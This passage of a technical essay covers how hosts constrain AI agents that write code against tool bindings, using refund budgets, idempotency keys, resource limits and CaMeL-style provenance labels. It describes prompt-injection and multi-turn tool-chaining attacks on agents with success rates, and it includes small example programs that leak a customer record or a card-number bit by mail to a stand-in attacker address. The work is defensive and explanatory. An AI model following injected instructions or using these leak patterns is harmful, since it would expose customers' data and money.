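| The developer | What each function does | Granting everything that any task might need |
| The user | What they want done | Accepting broad permissions because the choices are coarse or unfamiliar |
| The policy engine | The user's role and each tool's label | Granting the same powers for every task |
| A model that has seen only trusted input | What this request probably involves | Leaving out a necessary permission or adding a needless one |

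None of these is a good sole judge, but a host can combine them so that each can only narrow what the others allow:

grant = developer ∩ user ∩ policy ∩ model

For the support company, the developer caps refunds at 50 dollars, and the policy lets only senior staff issue them. The user asks for a 10-dollar refund for each late delivery. From that request, the model chooses bindings for refunds and replies but not for customer records. If it later reads a hidden instruction to fetch a customer's record, it has no binding that can do so. The model's choice is safe only if it is made before the model reads any tickets, because hidden instructions in them could influence it.

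The drawback of narrow grants is that mistakenly leaving out one needed permission blocks the task. An overly broad grant causes no trouble until someone exploits it, so developers who judge a system by completed tasks will tend to grant too much. If narrow grants block tasks too often, users may also turn off the restrictions or approve every request.

Asking a person is probably the safest way to widen a grant, and CapScope can do this outside its experiment. The host should show that person the exact capability, such as "refund up to 50 dollars on order A-1042", rather than rely on the model's explanation, which a hidden instruction may have shaped.

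## What harm can a program do with permitted calls alone?

Suppose the support company has kept its grant fairly narrow. The program may refund up to 50 dollars on any order with an open ticket, the host checks every amount, and the network is closed. The model then writes:

```javascript
const open = await tickets.list();
for (const t of open) {
  await refunds.issue(t.orderId, 50);
}
```

If 1,000 tickets are open, the company loses a lot of money:

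1,000 × $50 = $50,000

Each call names a real order and an amount that the schema allows. The host checks each call separately, so it allows the thousandth refund just as it allowed the first. The model might write this loop because of a hidden instruction in a ticket or by mistake, as with the misspelt field name that kept every ticket in the list.

### Three more kinds of damage

A program can leak data by combining a harmless read with a harmless message, as with the reply that contained the text of nine other tickets. Both calls satisfy their schemas, because the read schema doesn't restrict messages and the message schema accepts any text.

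A program can also do harm by acting on old information, even when it hasn't waited hours for approval. Suppose a customer complains twice about the same 60-dollar order, and two programs handle the two tickets at the same time. Both read the order before either issues a refund, so each finds that nobody has refunded it and refunds 50 dollars. The customer receives 100 dollars for a 60-dollar order.

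A batch can also fail halfway for reasons that no type checker could detect in advance. Say the company really does owe 1,000 customers 50 dollars each, and the payment service stops responding after 400 refunds. In agents that write code, the model usually reads the error, revises the program and runs it again, until a run succeeds or the agent reaches a retry limit, according to *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026). If the revised program starts again with the first customer, the 400 duplicate refunds cost the company 20,000 dollars.

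### Why a better schema can't prevent this

A schema is a test that takes one call and returns true or false. If a program's trace consists of the calls c₁ to cₙ and S is the schema's test, a host that checks every call guarantees:

S(c₁) and S(c₂) and … and S(cₙ)

This is a real guarantee, and it holds however strangely the program combines its calls. But a budget of 500 dollars is a statement about all the amounts together:

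a₁ + a₂ + … + aₙ ≤ 500

A test that checks each call separately cannot enforce that budget unless it refuses all refunds. If it accepts one refund, it also accepts the same refund a thousand times in a row.

The same reasoning applies to the order of calls. A test that accepts a lookup and a message individually will accept them in either order, so it can't allow a message before the lookup and forbid one after it.

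Checks that go beyond the schema have the same limit if they look at one call at a time. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined three toolkits for building agents: LangChain with LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's Agent Toolkit. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent gets, but none checks by default whether the agent may use the particular account or amount in a call.

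Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, checks arguments against lists of approved values and sets a ceiling on payments. It rejected all 48 disguised or malformed calls in a test suite. The same suite had earlier exposed a bug that let `NaN` past the ceiling. But the ceiling applies to each payment separately, so ScopeGate would allow the refund loop if the approved list contained all 1,000 orders.

### What a host can stop by remembering earlier calls

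A host that keeps a record of past calls can do more. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), worked out how much more. He considers a monitor that watches a program's steps and stops the program when the next step would break a policy. The monitor can remember everything the program has done. It doesn't know what the program will do next, or what it would have done with different data. Schneider shows that such a monitor can enforce a policy only if the policy meets three conditions:

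1. It judges each run by itself, without comparing it with other runs.
2. Once a run has broken the policy, nothing the program does later can put that right.
3. Any run that breaks the policy does so after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet all three are called safety properties. The 500-dollar budget is one example, and access rules that depend on what a program did earlier are another (Basin et al., 2012).

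Schneider writes each policy as a simple machine that changes state as the program runs. His first example forbids sending a message after reading a file. The machine starts in a state that permits every step. When the program reads a file, the machine moves to a second state, which permits everything except sending. For the refund budget, the state is a single number the host stores, the total spent so far, *s*. A refund of *a* dollars changes *s* to *s* + *a* if that sum is at most 500. Otherwise the machine has no permitted transition, and the host stops the program.

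Such a monitor works only if it detects every relevant step. Schneider warns that a system may have many ways to send a message, some of them well hidden, and the policy's definition of sending has to include them all. For the support company, the definition would have to include the binding that fetches any web address.

The monitor would also miss the double refund if it kept a separate record for each program, because each record would contain one check and one refund, in the right order. If an employee had issued one of the refunds by hand, even a record shared by all programs wouldn't include that refund.

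The half-finished batch is a problem for a different reason. The company wants all 1,000 refunds to go through or none of them. This policy fails Schneider's second condition, because a run that has made 400 refunds is unacceptable if it stops there but becomes acceptable once it has made the other 600. A monitor that can only stop the program would have to prevent the first refund to be sure that no run ends halfway.

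### Why secrecy involves more than one run

Secrecy fails the first condition. Suppose a program looks up a customer's card number and then answers a stranger's ticket. If the card's last digit is odd, it writes "Thanks for your message"; if it is even, it writes "Thank you for your message". The log shows only a lookup and a polite reply. Nobody could find the leak from this log alone, because they would need to compare the reply with the one the program would have sent for another card.

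Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, give this distinction a precise form. A trace property is a set of acceptable traces, so one can check each trace separately. A hyperproperty is a set of acceptable systems, each represented by all the traces it can produce. Their main example is noninterference, which requires that the actions of people with access to secrets have no effect on what people without access can observe. For the support agent, a similar rule would be:

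If two runs differ only in customers' card numbers, strangers receive the same messages in both.

Removing possible runs from a system can't break a trace property, so a host that refuses extra refunds can't cause the budget to be exceeded. But removing runs can break secrecy. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit, with any of the three possible on each run. Its possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is. Restricting the system to the third option adds no new runs, but the output now reveals the secret.

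A monitor can still protect a secret by enforcing a stricter rule than secrecy requires, such as forbidding all messages once the program has read a customer's record. This would stop the leak, but it would also stop the loop that emails apologies for late deliveries, because that loop looks up each customer's address first. An interpreter that attaches provenance labels to values could make finer distinctions by checking whether a message contains anything from the record.

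### Attacks on agents that write code

Felendler and colleagues tested whether such harms occur in practice. They compared ordinary MCP agents, which make one tool call at a time, with agents that write a program to call the same tools. Both kinds worked on tasks from 10 of the 28 servers in a public benchmark, using GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-4.1 mini. The program-writing agents used fewer tokens and less time on average, and their results were about as good. They did worse on some tasks that involved three servers, typically because the model left out a condition when writing the program. An ordinary agent could sometimes recover from such an error at the next step.

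For the security part, Felendler and colleagues listed sixteen classes of attack in five phases:

- Two occur while the agent looks for tools, through misleading file names or tool names.
- Two occur while the model plans and writes the program.
- Three occur while the program runs and uses results that an attacker has altered.
- Three occur when results come back and corrupt the agent's later decisions.
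- Six describe the damage that hostile code can do once it runs, such as reading files, leaking data or escaping from the sandbox.

A program that can only call typed bindings should be much less exposed to most of the last six. The others don't require an escape. The researchers tried one of these from each of the first four phases on a database server they had built, which had tools for queries, user accounts and door access. They reported similar results with GPT-4o and GPT-4.1.

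| What the attacker controlled | What the agent did | Did it also affect ordinary tool calls? |
|---|---|---|
| The name and description of a file | Listed the people without access to a door instead of those with access | Yes |
| The description of a tool | Kept writing and running programs that failed | Yes |
| The result of a tool | Reported one person's access rights as another's | No |
| The text of an error message | Created an administrator account with full access | No |

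The first attack closely resembles the refund loop, since it changed only a query's condition. The query was valid, and the agent reported success. In the third attack, even a careful reader of the program would have found nothing wrong, because the error was in the data passed from one call to the next.

The two entries marked "No" are less convincing. An ordinary agent that received the wrong person's passkey could copy it into its next call, just as the program did. It also reads error messages and could follow an instruction in one. Felendler and colleagues argue that ordinary MCP treats errors as feedback and never turns them into new code, but a model doesn't need to write code to call a tool that creates an account. The difference may depend on how the researchers set up the two agents.

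The study is better evidence that these attacks are possible than of how common they would be, because it used a purpose-built server and models that are now old. The researchers proposed defences, including a separate language model that looks for instructions in tool descriptions, results and error messages. These blocked all four attacks in every trial, but nobody tested them against an attacker who knew about them.

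### Does writing code make the problem worse?

Tool calls that seem harmless separately can also cause harm together. Li, He and colleagues (2025) studied this in *STAC*, using agents that don't write programs. In their main example, a user asks an agent to compress an important document, then to delete the original because a compressed copy exists, and finally to clear out all compressed files. Each request sounds reasonable, but together they leave no copy of the document.

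The researchers generated 483 such cases automatically. One language model planned a chain of two to six calls in which only the last did harm, and another component ran the chain in a simulated environment to check that it worked. Other models then wrote requests that would lead an agent through the chain. The agent under test received a conversation in which it appeared to have already made the earlier calls, and the attacker had up to three attempts to get it to make the last one. Across eight models, the attacks succeeded in 91.2 percent of cases on average, and the agents openly refused in fewer than 4 percent.

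Several features of the test favoured the attacker:

- The attacker was the agent's own user, so this wasn't prompt injection. For the support company, it would correspond to a dishonest employee or a stolen account.
- The attacker knew the tools and the data, and could invent the earlier part of the conversation.
- The same model, GPT-4.1, planned the attacks and judged whether they had worked.

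The earlier steps also mattered less than the headline figure suggests. On 390 of the cases, a single request for the last step succeeded 72.8 percent of the time, compared with 95.1 percent for the full method. On 32 tasks with real MCP servers, where the attacker had to discover the data, the success rate fell to 35.5 percent, still almost three times the 12.5 percent that an attacker achieved without a prepared chain.

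Newer models didn't solve the problem. *AgentLAB* (Jiang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) extended the method and allowed the attacker up to 20 turns. The attack succeeded in 94.6 percent of cases against GPT-5.1 and 73.3 percent against Claude 4.5 Sonnet. The same Claude model resisted every attempt to insert a harmful task through the data it read. Models released since then may do better, but a model that has learned to recognise suspicious text won't necessarily notice that a series of ordinary requests has a bad result.

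So code didn't create the problem, but it does increase the speed and number of calls. Suppose a model takes three seconds to write each tool call, while a host can process each call from a program in a tenth of a second. A thousand refunds would take 50 minutes as separate calls and 100 seconds in a loop. An employee who noticed the problem after ten minutes could save 40,000 of the 50,000 dollars if the refunds were separate calls, but nothing if they ran in a loop.

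Programs also remove the model's chance to reconsider between calls. The results from Li and colleagues suggest that this chance gives little protection against a skilled attacker, because the models they tested had it and rarely used it to refuse. When they told GPT-4.1 to weigh harms and benefits before each call, the attack's success rate on the first attempt fell from 87.4 to 58.6 percent, but by the third attempt it was back at 86.7 percent. The chance to reconsider is probably more useful against honest mistakes. A model that sees "refund issued" for a customer whose parcel arrived on time may realise after one refund, instead of a thousand, that its filter is wrong.

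### Bindings that do more of the job

One remedy is to replace several small bindings with one that matches the task. The company could offer this function for late deliveries:

```
refunds.compensateLate(orderIds)   // 1 to 50 different orders, $10 each
```

The host fixes the amount and confirms from the courier's records that each order was late. A schema can limit the length of a list and require its items to be different, so one call can now pay out at most 50 × $10 = $500. This turns the budget into a limit on a single call, which a schema can express. The program could still call the function repeatedly, so the host should accept only one call per task.

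A similar binding can prevent leaks through messages. When the program calls `tickets.apologise(ticketId)`, the host looks up the address and sends a fixed text. The program can't add a customer's details to the message, so it can convey information only through its choice of tickets.

Such bindings take away some of the freedom that made code useful. If the company wants to give 15 dollars to customers who waited more than a week, a developer has to change the function. A coarse binding can also increase the harm, as the function that deletes all compressed files did in the last step of the STAC example. A binding should do one complete job and check the conditions for it, not just act on more things at once.

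### Guards that keep a running total

If the program needs to choose its own amounts, the host can use the kind of wrapper mentioned earlier, which stops at a total of 500 dollars. Written out, it could look like this:

```javascript
// runs in the host
function withBudget(issue, limit) {
  let spent = 0;
  return async (orderId, amount) => {
    checkAmount(amount);           // throws unless a whole number from 1 to 50
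    if (spent + amount > limit) throw new Error("budget used up");
    spent += amount;               // before paying
    return issue(orderId, amount);
  };
}
```

The host runs `spent += amount` before each payment because a program can start many calls without waiting for the first to finish. If the host updated the total only after each payment, a program could start 1,000 refunds while `spent` was still 0, and all of them would pass the limit check.

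The total also has to persist after the program ends. If the host creates a new guard for every run, the model can spend 500 dollars, write another program and spend 500 more. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) recommends storing authorisation as durable state outside the prompt, instead of inferring it from the conversation. For refunds, the host could keep a database record for each task and check and update it in one step, so that two machines can't spend the same money.

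Several recent systems build such limits into the permission. In *AGATE* (2026), a permission can have an expiry time, a maximum for each call, a maximum across all calls and a limit on the number of uses. In *ToolFence* (2026), a language model that sees only the user's request and the tool schemas writes a plan before the agent reads any outside data. The plan gives each permitted call a budget and can require an argument to come from a particular field of an earlier result. For the support company, the plan could require every order number to come from the ticket list. But the budget might be hard to choose, because nobody knows how many deliveries were late until someone reads the tickets.

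In *Agenra*, Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026) present a guard whose core they checked with the proof assistant Lean. In their example, an agent may send a report to Alice once, using the address from a trusted directory. The guard removes the permission before it runs the mail tool and doesn't restore it if the tool fails, because the message may have been sent anyway. This prevents duplicates, but Alice may never receive the report. The guard also handles one kind of outdated information by rejecting the old address if a later lookup returns a different one. Its proofs assume that calls arrive one at a time, so a host that accepts parallel calls would have to queue them.

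Guards that track earlier calls are harder to change than schemas. Suppose an agent may delete file B once and file A once, and the guard uses the first permission that fits. If a developer widens the first permission to cover either file, deleting A first uses up that permission and leaves only the one for A. The agent can then delete A again but not B. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues wrote 51 such changes to test their checks, which approved all 21 that left the intended tasks working and none of the 30 that broke one. A change can pass these checks and still be unwise. For example, allowing a second message to Alice breaks no task, but it permits the duplicate that the original rule was meant to prevent.

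### Planning first and acting later

A host can also look at the whole batch before anything happens. Instead of issuing refunds, the program submits a list:

```javascript
const plan = late.map(t => ({ orderId: t.orderId, amount: 10 }));
return await refunds.propose(plan);
```

The host can now check the total, look for duplicates and compare the orders with the courier's records. If a person has to approve the batch, they see "30 refunds, $300 in total" and decide once instead of thirty times. A proposal for 1,000 refunds totaling $50,000 would be easy to notice. The host should then carry out the stored list, not a new one from the program.

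Cloudflare's file library for its isolates works similarly. Varda and colleagues explain that a program calls `planEdits` with a list of changes, then `applyEditPlan` to carry them out. In their example, the program makes the second call directly after the first, so nobody reviews the plan. A company that wanted a review would give the program only `planEdits` and keep `applyEditPlan` in the host.

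Information can go out of date between the plan and the action, so the host should repeat the important checks when it issues the refund. For the 60-dollar order, it can read the amount already refunded and record the new refund in a single database step. The second program's request would then fail, because only 10 dollars remain. The program's own check still helps avoid pointless requests, but the company no longer relies on it.

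### Batches that succeed or fail together

Cloudflare's library also undoes the earlier writes in a batch by default if a later one fails, so a model that runs the batch again starts from the original files. Databases have long offered such transactions. The limit that Schneider found for monitors does not apply to them, because the host can reverse what the program has already done as well as stop it.

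This works because Cloudflare's library controls the storage. The support company can't reverse a payment in the same way, and Cloudflare's undo functions for individual calls help only if the payment service offers a way to cancel a refund. A more dependable method is to make repetition harmless. Many payment services accept an idempotency key, a label that identifies a request. If a second request arrives with the same label, the service returns the first result and doesn't pay again. The host could build the label from the order number and the reason for the refund:

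```javascript
const key = `late-delivery:${orderId}`;
```

After a failure at customer 400, the model can run the whole program again. The first 400 requests have no further effect, and the remaining 600 customers get their money. The host has to choose the label, because a program that generated one at random would produce a different label on each run. ScopeGate similarly takes the label from trusted context and refuses sensitive calls without one. If a response goes missing, the host can safely repeat the request without knowing whether the first one arrived. For refunds, this is better than Agenra's rule, which uses up the permission and could leave a customer unpaid.

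Nobody can take back an email, so the host should delay it. It can queue the messages and send them only after the refunds have gone through, marking off each one as it is sent. If the program fails before then, no customer will have received an apology that mentions a refund that was never made. The host can also check the queued messages together, and might find that one contains text from nine other tickets. But the program can't wait for a reply to a message the host hasn't sent, so queuing suits notifications better than conversations.

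## How are running time, memory and the number of calls limited?

Hosts set separate limits on computing time, total time, memory, nested function calls, output and binding calls, because a program can reach one limit while staying far below the others. A guard that counts dollars doesn't stop a program from running forever or filling the server's memory. A model could write an endless loop by mistake or because of an instruction hidden in a ticket.

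### Computing time and waiting time

CPU time is the time a processor spends executing the program. Wall-clock time also includes waiting. Consider two ways to refund 1,000 open tickets:

```javascript
// one after another
for (const t of open) await refunds.issue(t.orderId, 50);

// all at once
await Promise.all(open.map(t => refunds.issue(t.orderId, 50)));
```

Suppose the payment service takes two seconds per refund. The loop runs for more than half an hour but spends nearly all of that time waiting, so a 30-second CPU limit wouldn't stop it. A 30-second wall-clock limit would stop it after about 15 refunds. The one-line version starts every refund without waiting for any to finish. If starting a call takes 0.01 milliseconds of CPU time, starting all 1,000 takes 10 milliseconds, so neither limit would prevent any of the refunds from being started.

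Cloudflare's *Limits* gives Workers on the paid plan 30 seconds of CPU time per web request, which developers can raise to five minutes. The average Worker uses about 2.2 milliseconds. Waiting for a network or database doesn't count, and a Worker can wait as long as the client stays connected. Dynamic Workers inherit these limits, but the host can lower them when it loads the program:

```javascript
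limits: { cpuMs: 50, subRequests: 30 },
```

A program that reaches either number immediately gets an exception. Cloudflare also gives each Code Mode run a timeout, 30 seconds by default.

Monty's clock likewise stops while a program waits for the host. According to Pydantic's *Resource Limits*, a host function that takes a minute uses none of the program's time budget. Monty allows 1,000 calls by default, so a program making one-minute calls could wait nearly 17 hours and use almost none of its budget. Pydantic also offers a wall-clock deadline, but it restarts after every call, so the host has to enforce any time limit on the whole task itself.

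Ada, which sells customer-support agents, limits each run of a code tool to about 5 seconds of computing time, about 65 seconds in total, and 10 network requests, according to its *Limits and best practices*.

| Budget | Dynamic Workers, paid plan | Monty |
|---|---|---|
| Computing time | 30 seconds by default, 5 minutes at most | Unlimited unless the host sets a limit |
| Total time | Unlimited for web requests, but 30 seconds by default in Code Mode | No limit for a whole program |
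| Memory | 128 MB per isolate | Unlimited unless the host sets a limit |
| Nested function calls | V8's built-in limit | 1,000 by default |
| Outside calls | 10,000 subrequests by default | 1,000 by default |
| Output | 256 KB of log data per request | 10 MiB by default in Pydantic's print collectors |

*DADL* limits composites, the fixed programs that developers store as tools. Its runtime kills a composite after 30 seconds by default and 120 seconds at most, and caps the number of API calls to stop runaway loops. Programs that the model writes also get a hard timeout and a call cap.

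Output needs a limit because printed text takes up the host's memory and, if the host passes it on, the model's context. But a limit can hide evidence. Cloudflare stops recording a request's log data after 256 KB, so a hostile program could print junk first to keep its later messages out of the log. The host should therefore record binding calls separately from printed output.

### Stopping a program that never pauses

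A program in an endless loop never returns control to the host, so the engine has to interrupt it. In V8, another thread can request termination. The running code checks for such requests when it enters a function or repeats a loop, and if it finds one, V8 raises an exception that the program can't catch.

Monty's interpreter reads the clock at every 256th instruction, as Pydantic's *Resource limits*, a more technical page, explains. Some single instructions do a great deal of work, so Monty also checks the clock inside many of them. One documented gap involves nested pairs. Suppose a program starts with an empty tuple `x` and replaces it with `(x, x)` fifty times. The result takes up little memory because both halves of each pair are the same object. But a comparison of two such structures follows every path through them:

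2⁵⁰ ≈ 10¹⁵ paths

At a billion paths per second, this would take about 13 days. Monty checks the clock after every 64 items in a container, and a pair has only two, so the time limit never takes effect. The comparison ends only when the wall-clock deadline outside the interpreter kills the worker process.

WebAssembly engines can limit a program by counting instructions instead of time. In Wasmtime, a widely used engine, the host gives a program a number of units called fuel. Nearly every instruction uses one unit, and the engine interrupts the program when none remain. Wasmtime's documentation describes fuel as completely deterministic, meaning that the same program with the same fuel always stops at the same point, which makes a failure easy to reproduce.

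The counting slows programs down, so Wasmtime also offers a faster method based on a shared counter, called the epoch, that the host advances at intervals. The program compares this counter with a limit only when it enters a function or repeats a loop (cfallin, 2022, *Add epoch-based interruption for coop*). These checks slow the program by around 10 percent, according to Wasmtime's *Interrupting Wasm Execution*. However, the same program may be interrupted at a different point each time it runs, or not at all. With either method, the host can end the program or pause it and decide later whether to resume it.

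Fuel measures how much computation a program does and doesn't reflect the effects of its calls. A participant in a discussion archived by the Bytecode Alliance (2022), the organisation behind Wasmtime, explains that a call to a host function uses one unit of fuel unless the host deducts more. By default, a call that issues a 50-dollar refund therefore uses as much fuel as an addition. A host could deduct 1,000 units per refund, so that a budget of 10,000 units allows at most ten refunds, but a separate counter would be clearer.

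Some languages prevent endless loops. Starlark, a small language similar to Python that Google's build tool Bazel uses for configuration, has no `while` loop and forbids recursion. Its `for` loops only go through finite collections, so every program eventually ends. But a program can still run for a very long time, since four nested loops, each over 1,000 items, take 10¹² steps. The loop that refunds 1,000 tickets would also be legal in Starlark. Starlark programs therefore still need a time limit and a call limit.

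### Counting memory

An early version of Monty limited how many times a program could request memory, according to Mintlify's copy of the documentation. This count is a poor measure of how much memory a program requests, because the expression `[0] * 100_000_000` can request hundreds of megabytes at once, while a program that builds many short strings makes thousands of tiny requests. The current documentation no longer lists this limit, and Monty now counts the bytes requested.

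The memory limit works in three ways:

- For many operations, Monty can calculate the size of the result beforehand. It refuses `'x' * 10**12` before reserving any memory.
- When a program crosses the limit during other operations, the interpreter stops it at the next check, and the worker survives.
- If memory use jumps past a higher limit before the next check, the worker process exits and the host replaces it.

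Passing data between program and host takes extra memory, because Monty briefly holds about three copies of it. A program with a 30 MB limit can therefore pass at most about 10 MB in one value.

Cloudflare's 128 MB memory limit applies to a whole isolate, which may be serving several requests at once. When an isolate exceeds the limit, the runtime lets requests in progress finish and creates a new isolate for later ones. Running each program in a fresh isolate keeps one program's memory use from affecting another program.

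Function calls that never return also use up memory. Monty raises an error at 1,000 nested calls by default. The program can catch this error and continue, but it can't catch the errors for exceeding time or memory limits.

### A cap on refunds

An engine's call limits are meant to stop runaway programs, and the defaults are far too high to prevent large financial losses. Monty's default of 1,000 calls would allow nearly 50,000 dollars in refunds. Monty also counts every kind of request to the host, so a limit low enough to restrict refunds would prevent the program from looking up customers. Cloudflare defines a subrequest as a web request or a call to one of its own services, such as a database. It isn't clear that a call to a binding the host wrote counts as one. Even if it did, the default would allow 10,000 refunds worth 500,000 dollars.

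The support company should therefore count refunds in the refund binding itself. If the binding accepts 20 per run, the most a run can cost is:

20 × $50 = $1,000

This limit applies to both versions of the program above, whatever the model's reason for writing them. But it applies to each run separately, like a dollar budget that resets with each program, so fifty runs could cost 50,000 dollars, as much as the original loop.

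Monty has the same weakness when a host saves a paused program. The restored program keeps its call limit, but the call count goes back to zero. If the company saved the program at each refund to wait for approval, the count might never reach the limit. The limit on computing time is safer because the saved program includes the time already used.

The host therefore has to store the count outside the run, as with the dollar total. This version allows each employee's agents 20 refunds in any 24 hours:

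```javascript
// runs in the host
async function issueLimited(userId, orderId, amount) {
  checkAmount(amount);
  const key = `late-delivery:${orderId}`;
  const ok = await quota.reserve(userId, key, { max: 20, hours: 24 });
  if (!ok) throw new Error("refund limit reached");
  return payments.refund(orderId, amount, { idempotencyKey: key });
}
```

`quota.reserve` stands for a database operation that, in one step, counts the employee's recent refunds and adds the new one if the quota allows it. The host fills in `userId` from the employee's login, because a program that could set `userId` could start a new quota by changing it.

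The company also needs a limit for all agents together, because if ten employees' agents read the same poisoned ticket, they could lose 10,000 dollars in a day even if each stayed within its employee's limit. A rolling 24-hour window prevents an agent from issuing 20 refunds at 11:59 p.m. and 20 more two minutes later, which it could do with a quota that resets at midnight. Dash0 uses a rolling window for the credits its automated workflows spend. It starts no new run once the budget is used up, and aborts a running one as soon as it would exceed the budget.

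Such limits will sometimes block legitimate work. In the week when thirty deliveries were late, a quota of 20 would leave ten customers without their 10 dollars. When the quota runs out, the binding should return an ordinary error instead of killing the program, so that the program can report which customers are still waiting and an employee can raise the limit. Similarly, in NVIDIA's Data Designer software, once a model has used up its tool calls, further calls return a message explaining the limit, and the model can still write an answer.

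### When time runs out halfway

A time limit usually can't end so gently. Suppose the company has raised the quota to 30, and the program refunds the thirty customers one after another. Listing the tickets takes one second, each refund takes two, and the host kills the program after 30 seconds. At that moment:

- Fourteen customers have their money.
- The host has sent the fifteenth refund to the payment service but hasn't received an answer.
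- The program hasn't requested the other fifteen.

Killing the program doesn't reverse the completed refunds or recall the request in progress. If the program had started all thirty refunds at once, the host might have no result for any of them. The program also can't report how far it got, because it is killed before it reaches its last line.

An example in DADL's *Use Composites* would have the same problem. The composite creates a project, applies a template, changes the settings and returns the project. If the runtime killed it after the first call, the project would exist with the wrong settings, and the model wouldn't have its ID. Running the composite again would probably create a second project.

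The model shouldn't rely on variables left over from the stopped program. Pydantic warns that a program stopped by a time or memory limit may leave damaged data behind, and that execution "is not transactional". The session still accepts new code, so the host has to discard the session. Otherwise, the model's next program might read a list called `refunded` that is missing the last customer. The host's own record is more reliable if the host writes "pending" before it sends each refund and "done" after the answer arrives.

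Each refund carries an idempotency key, so the model can safely rerun the whole program even though nobody knows whether the fifteenth refund went through. This works only while the payment service still stores the keys. It may not store them for long, so the host should check its own record before repeating an old request.

Repeated requests shouldn't count toward the quota. Suppose the limit is 20 and the host kills the program after its fifteenth request. If the quota counted every request, the second run would use the remaining five on customers who had already been paid. `quota.reserve` counts each key only once, so the second run can pay five new customers.

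Software that retries requests automatically needs the same keys. *DADL*'s runtime, for example, can repeat a request after certain errors. Cloudflare's workflows store the result of each completed step and don't run that step again. But a workflow could fail after a refund goes through but before it stores the result. The step would then run again, and only the key would prevent a second refund.

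## Can the interpreter track where data came from?

Quotas limit how much a program can do, but a single email can leak a customer's record. Forbidding all messages after a lookup would also stop harmless ones, such as an apology. An interpreter can be more precise if it attaches a provenance label to every value, recording where the value came from and who may receive it. The host can then refuse only the messages that contain a customer's record.

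The best-known system of this kind is CaMeL ("Capabilities for Machine Learning"), which Google DeepMind presented in 2025. Its capabilities are labels on data, unlike those in Miller's work, which are references that grant a right to act.

### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL builds on the dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model can use tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. The quarantined model's answers go into variables, which the privileged model can pass to a tool by name without seeing their contents. A hidden instruction in a ticket therefore can't make the privileged model add a refund.

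*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes a flaw that DeepMind researchers found in Willison's own design. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, but the quarantined model has to read the address from the notes. If an attacker has hidden an instruction in the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address, and the agent would then send the document to the wrong person even though the plan was correct.

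CaMeL therefore checks the data as well as the plan:

1. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted version of Python.
2. A purpose-built interpreter runs the program one operation at a time.
3. When the program needs a fact from untrusted text, it asks the quarantined model and specifies the type of answer, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter labels each value. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain that the label lists the value's sources and its permitted readers.
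5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their labels. The policy allows or denies the call and gives a reason.

Willison notes that the design also improves privacy. The company that provides the privileged model never receives the tools' results, and the quarantined model's task is easier, so a smaller model on the user's own computer might be able to do it.

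### A refused email, line by line

Suppose an employee tells the support agent: "Customer C-88 wants a copy of her record. Find the address she gives in her ticket and send it there." A stranger has opened another ticket and hidden a request in it to send C-88's record to `thief@attacker.example`. The privileged model hasn't seen either ticket. In simplified form, it writes:

```python
all_tickets = tickets_list()
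address = ask_quarantined(
    "Which email address does customer C-88 give?",
    all_tickets, EmailAddress)
record = customers_get("C-88")
mail_send(address, record)
```

The hidden request misleads the quarantined model, which returns the stranger's address. The labels then develop as follows:

| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `all_tickets` | Anyone who can open a ticket | Support staff |
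| `address` | Anyone who can open a ticket | Support staff |
| `record` | The customer database | Support staff and C-88's registered address |

The company's developers specify the labels for tickets and records. The interpreter works out the label for `address`, which inherits everything from the tickets because the quarantined model read them. When the program reaches its last line, the interpreter runs the policy for `mail_send`:

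```python
def mail_send_policy(to, body):
    if to.value not in body.readers:
        return Denied("this recipient may not read the message")
    return Allowed()
```

The stranger's address isn't among the record's allowed readers, so the interpreter refuses the call. A schema would have accepted the call, because `thief@attacker.example` is a well-formed address.

If the quarantined model had returned C-88's registered address, this policy would have allowed the email. In Willison's example, the policy instead checks whether the recipient's address is already trusted under the user's policies. An email to a trusted address goes out without a prompt, even if the address came from an untrusted email. For any other address, the system can ask the user to approve the message.

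Labels also stop the leak in which a program pastes other customers' tickets into a reply. When a program combines two values, the result keeps the sources of both but only the readers they share. If staff and Ana may read one ticket, and staff and Ben may read another, the readers of the combined text are:

{staff, Ana} ∩ {staff, Ben} = {staff}

The program can't send that text to either customer.

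Tracking where data came from works only if the interpreter carries labels through every operation. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found that when a program inserted an untrusted value into text, as programs that write emails routinely do, CaMeL's interpreter treated the result as trusted.

### When the call itself reveals a secret

A program can leak a secret without putting it into any argument:

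```python
record = customers_get("C-88")
if record.card_number % 2 == 1:
    mail_send("thief@attacker.example", "Hello")
```

The word "Hello" is public, so a policy that checks only the arguments allows the call. But the stranger receives an email only if the card number is odd. This is an implicit flow, and like the differently worded thank-you messages earlier, it doesn't show up in the log of a single run.

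To close this gap, the interpreter also has to track control dependence, meaning which values determine whether a line runs. When the program enters the `if` block, the interpreter adds the condition's label to everything inside. The policy check for `mail_send` then detects that the call depends on a card number the stranger may not read. *PolicySniff* (2026) explains that CaMeL has a strict mode that does this. This mode also covers errors, because an error caused by a secret value can prevent a later call, and the missing call reveals something about the secret.

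A stranger can't get the privileged model to write such a program, because the model receives only the employee's request. An employee seems more likely to cause one by accident. For example, if an employee asks the agent to email the courier about every customer with a premium account, the courier learns which customers have one.

Strict tracking also blocks useful work. In the loop that gives 10 dollars for each late delivery, the customers' tickets determine which refunds the program issues. The interpreter therefore marks every refund as depending on untrusted data, even if its order number and amount are correct. A policy that forbids payments that depend on untrusted data would block all thirty refunds.

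Even strict mode missed some implicit flows. Garby and colleagues adapted a program from the 1970s to show how. With the card number as the secret, it looks like this:

```python
odd = True
tmp = True
if record.card_number % 2 == 1:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    odd = False
if odd:
    mail_send("thief@attacker.example", "Hello")
```

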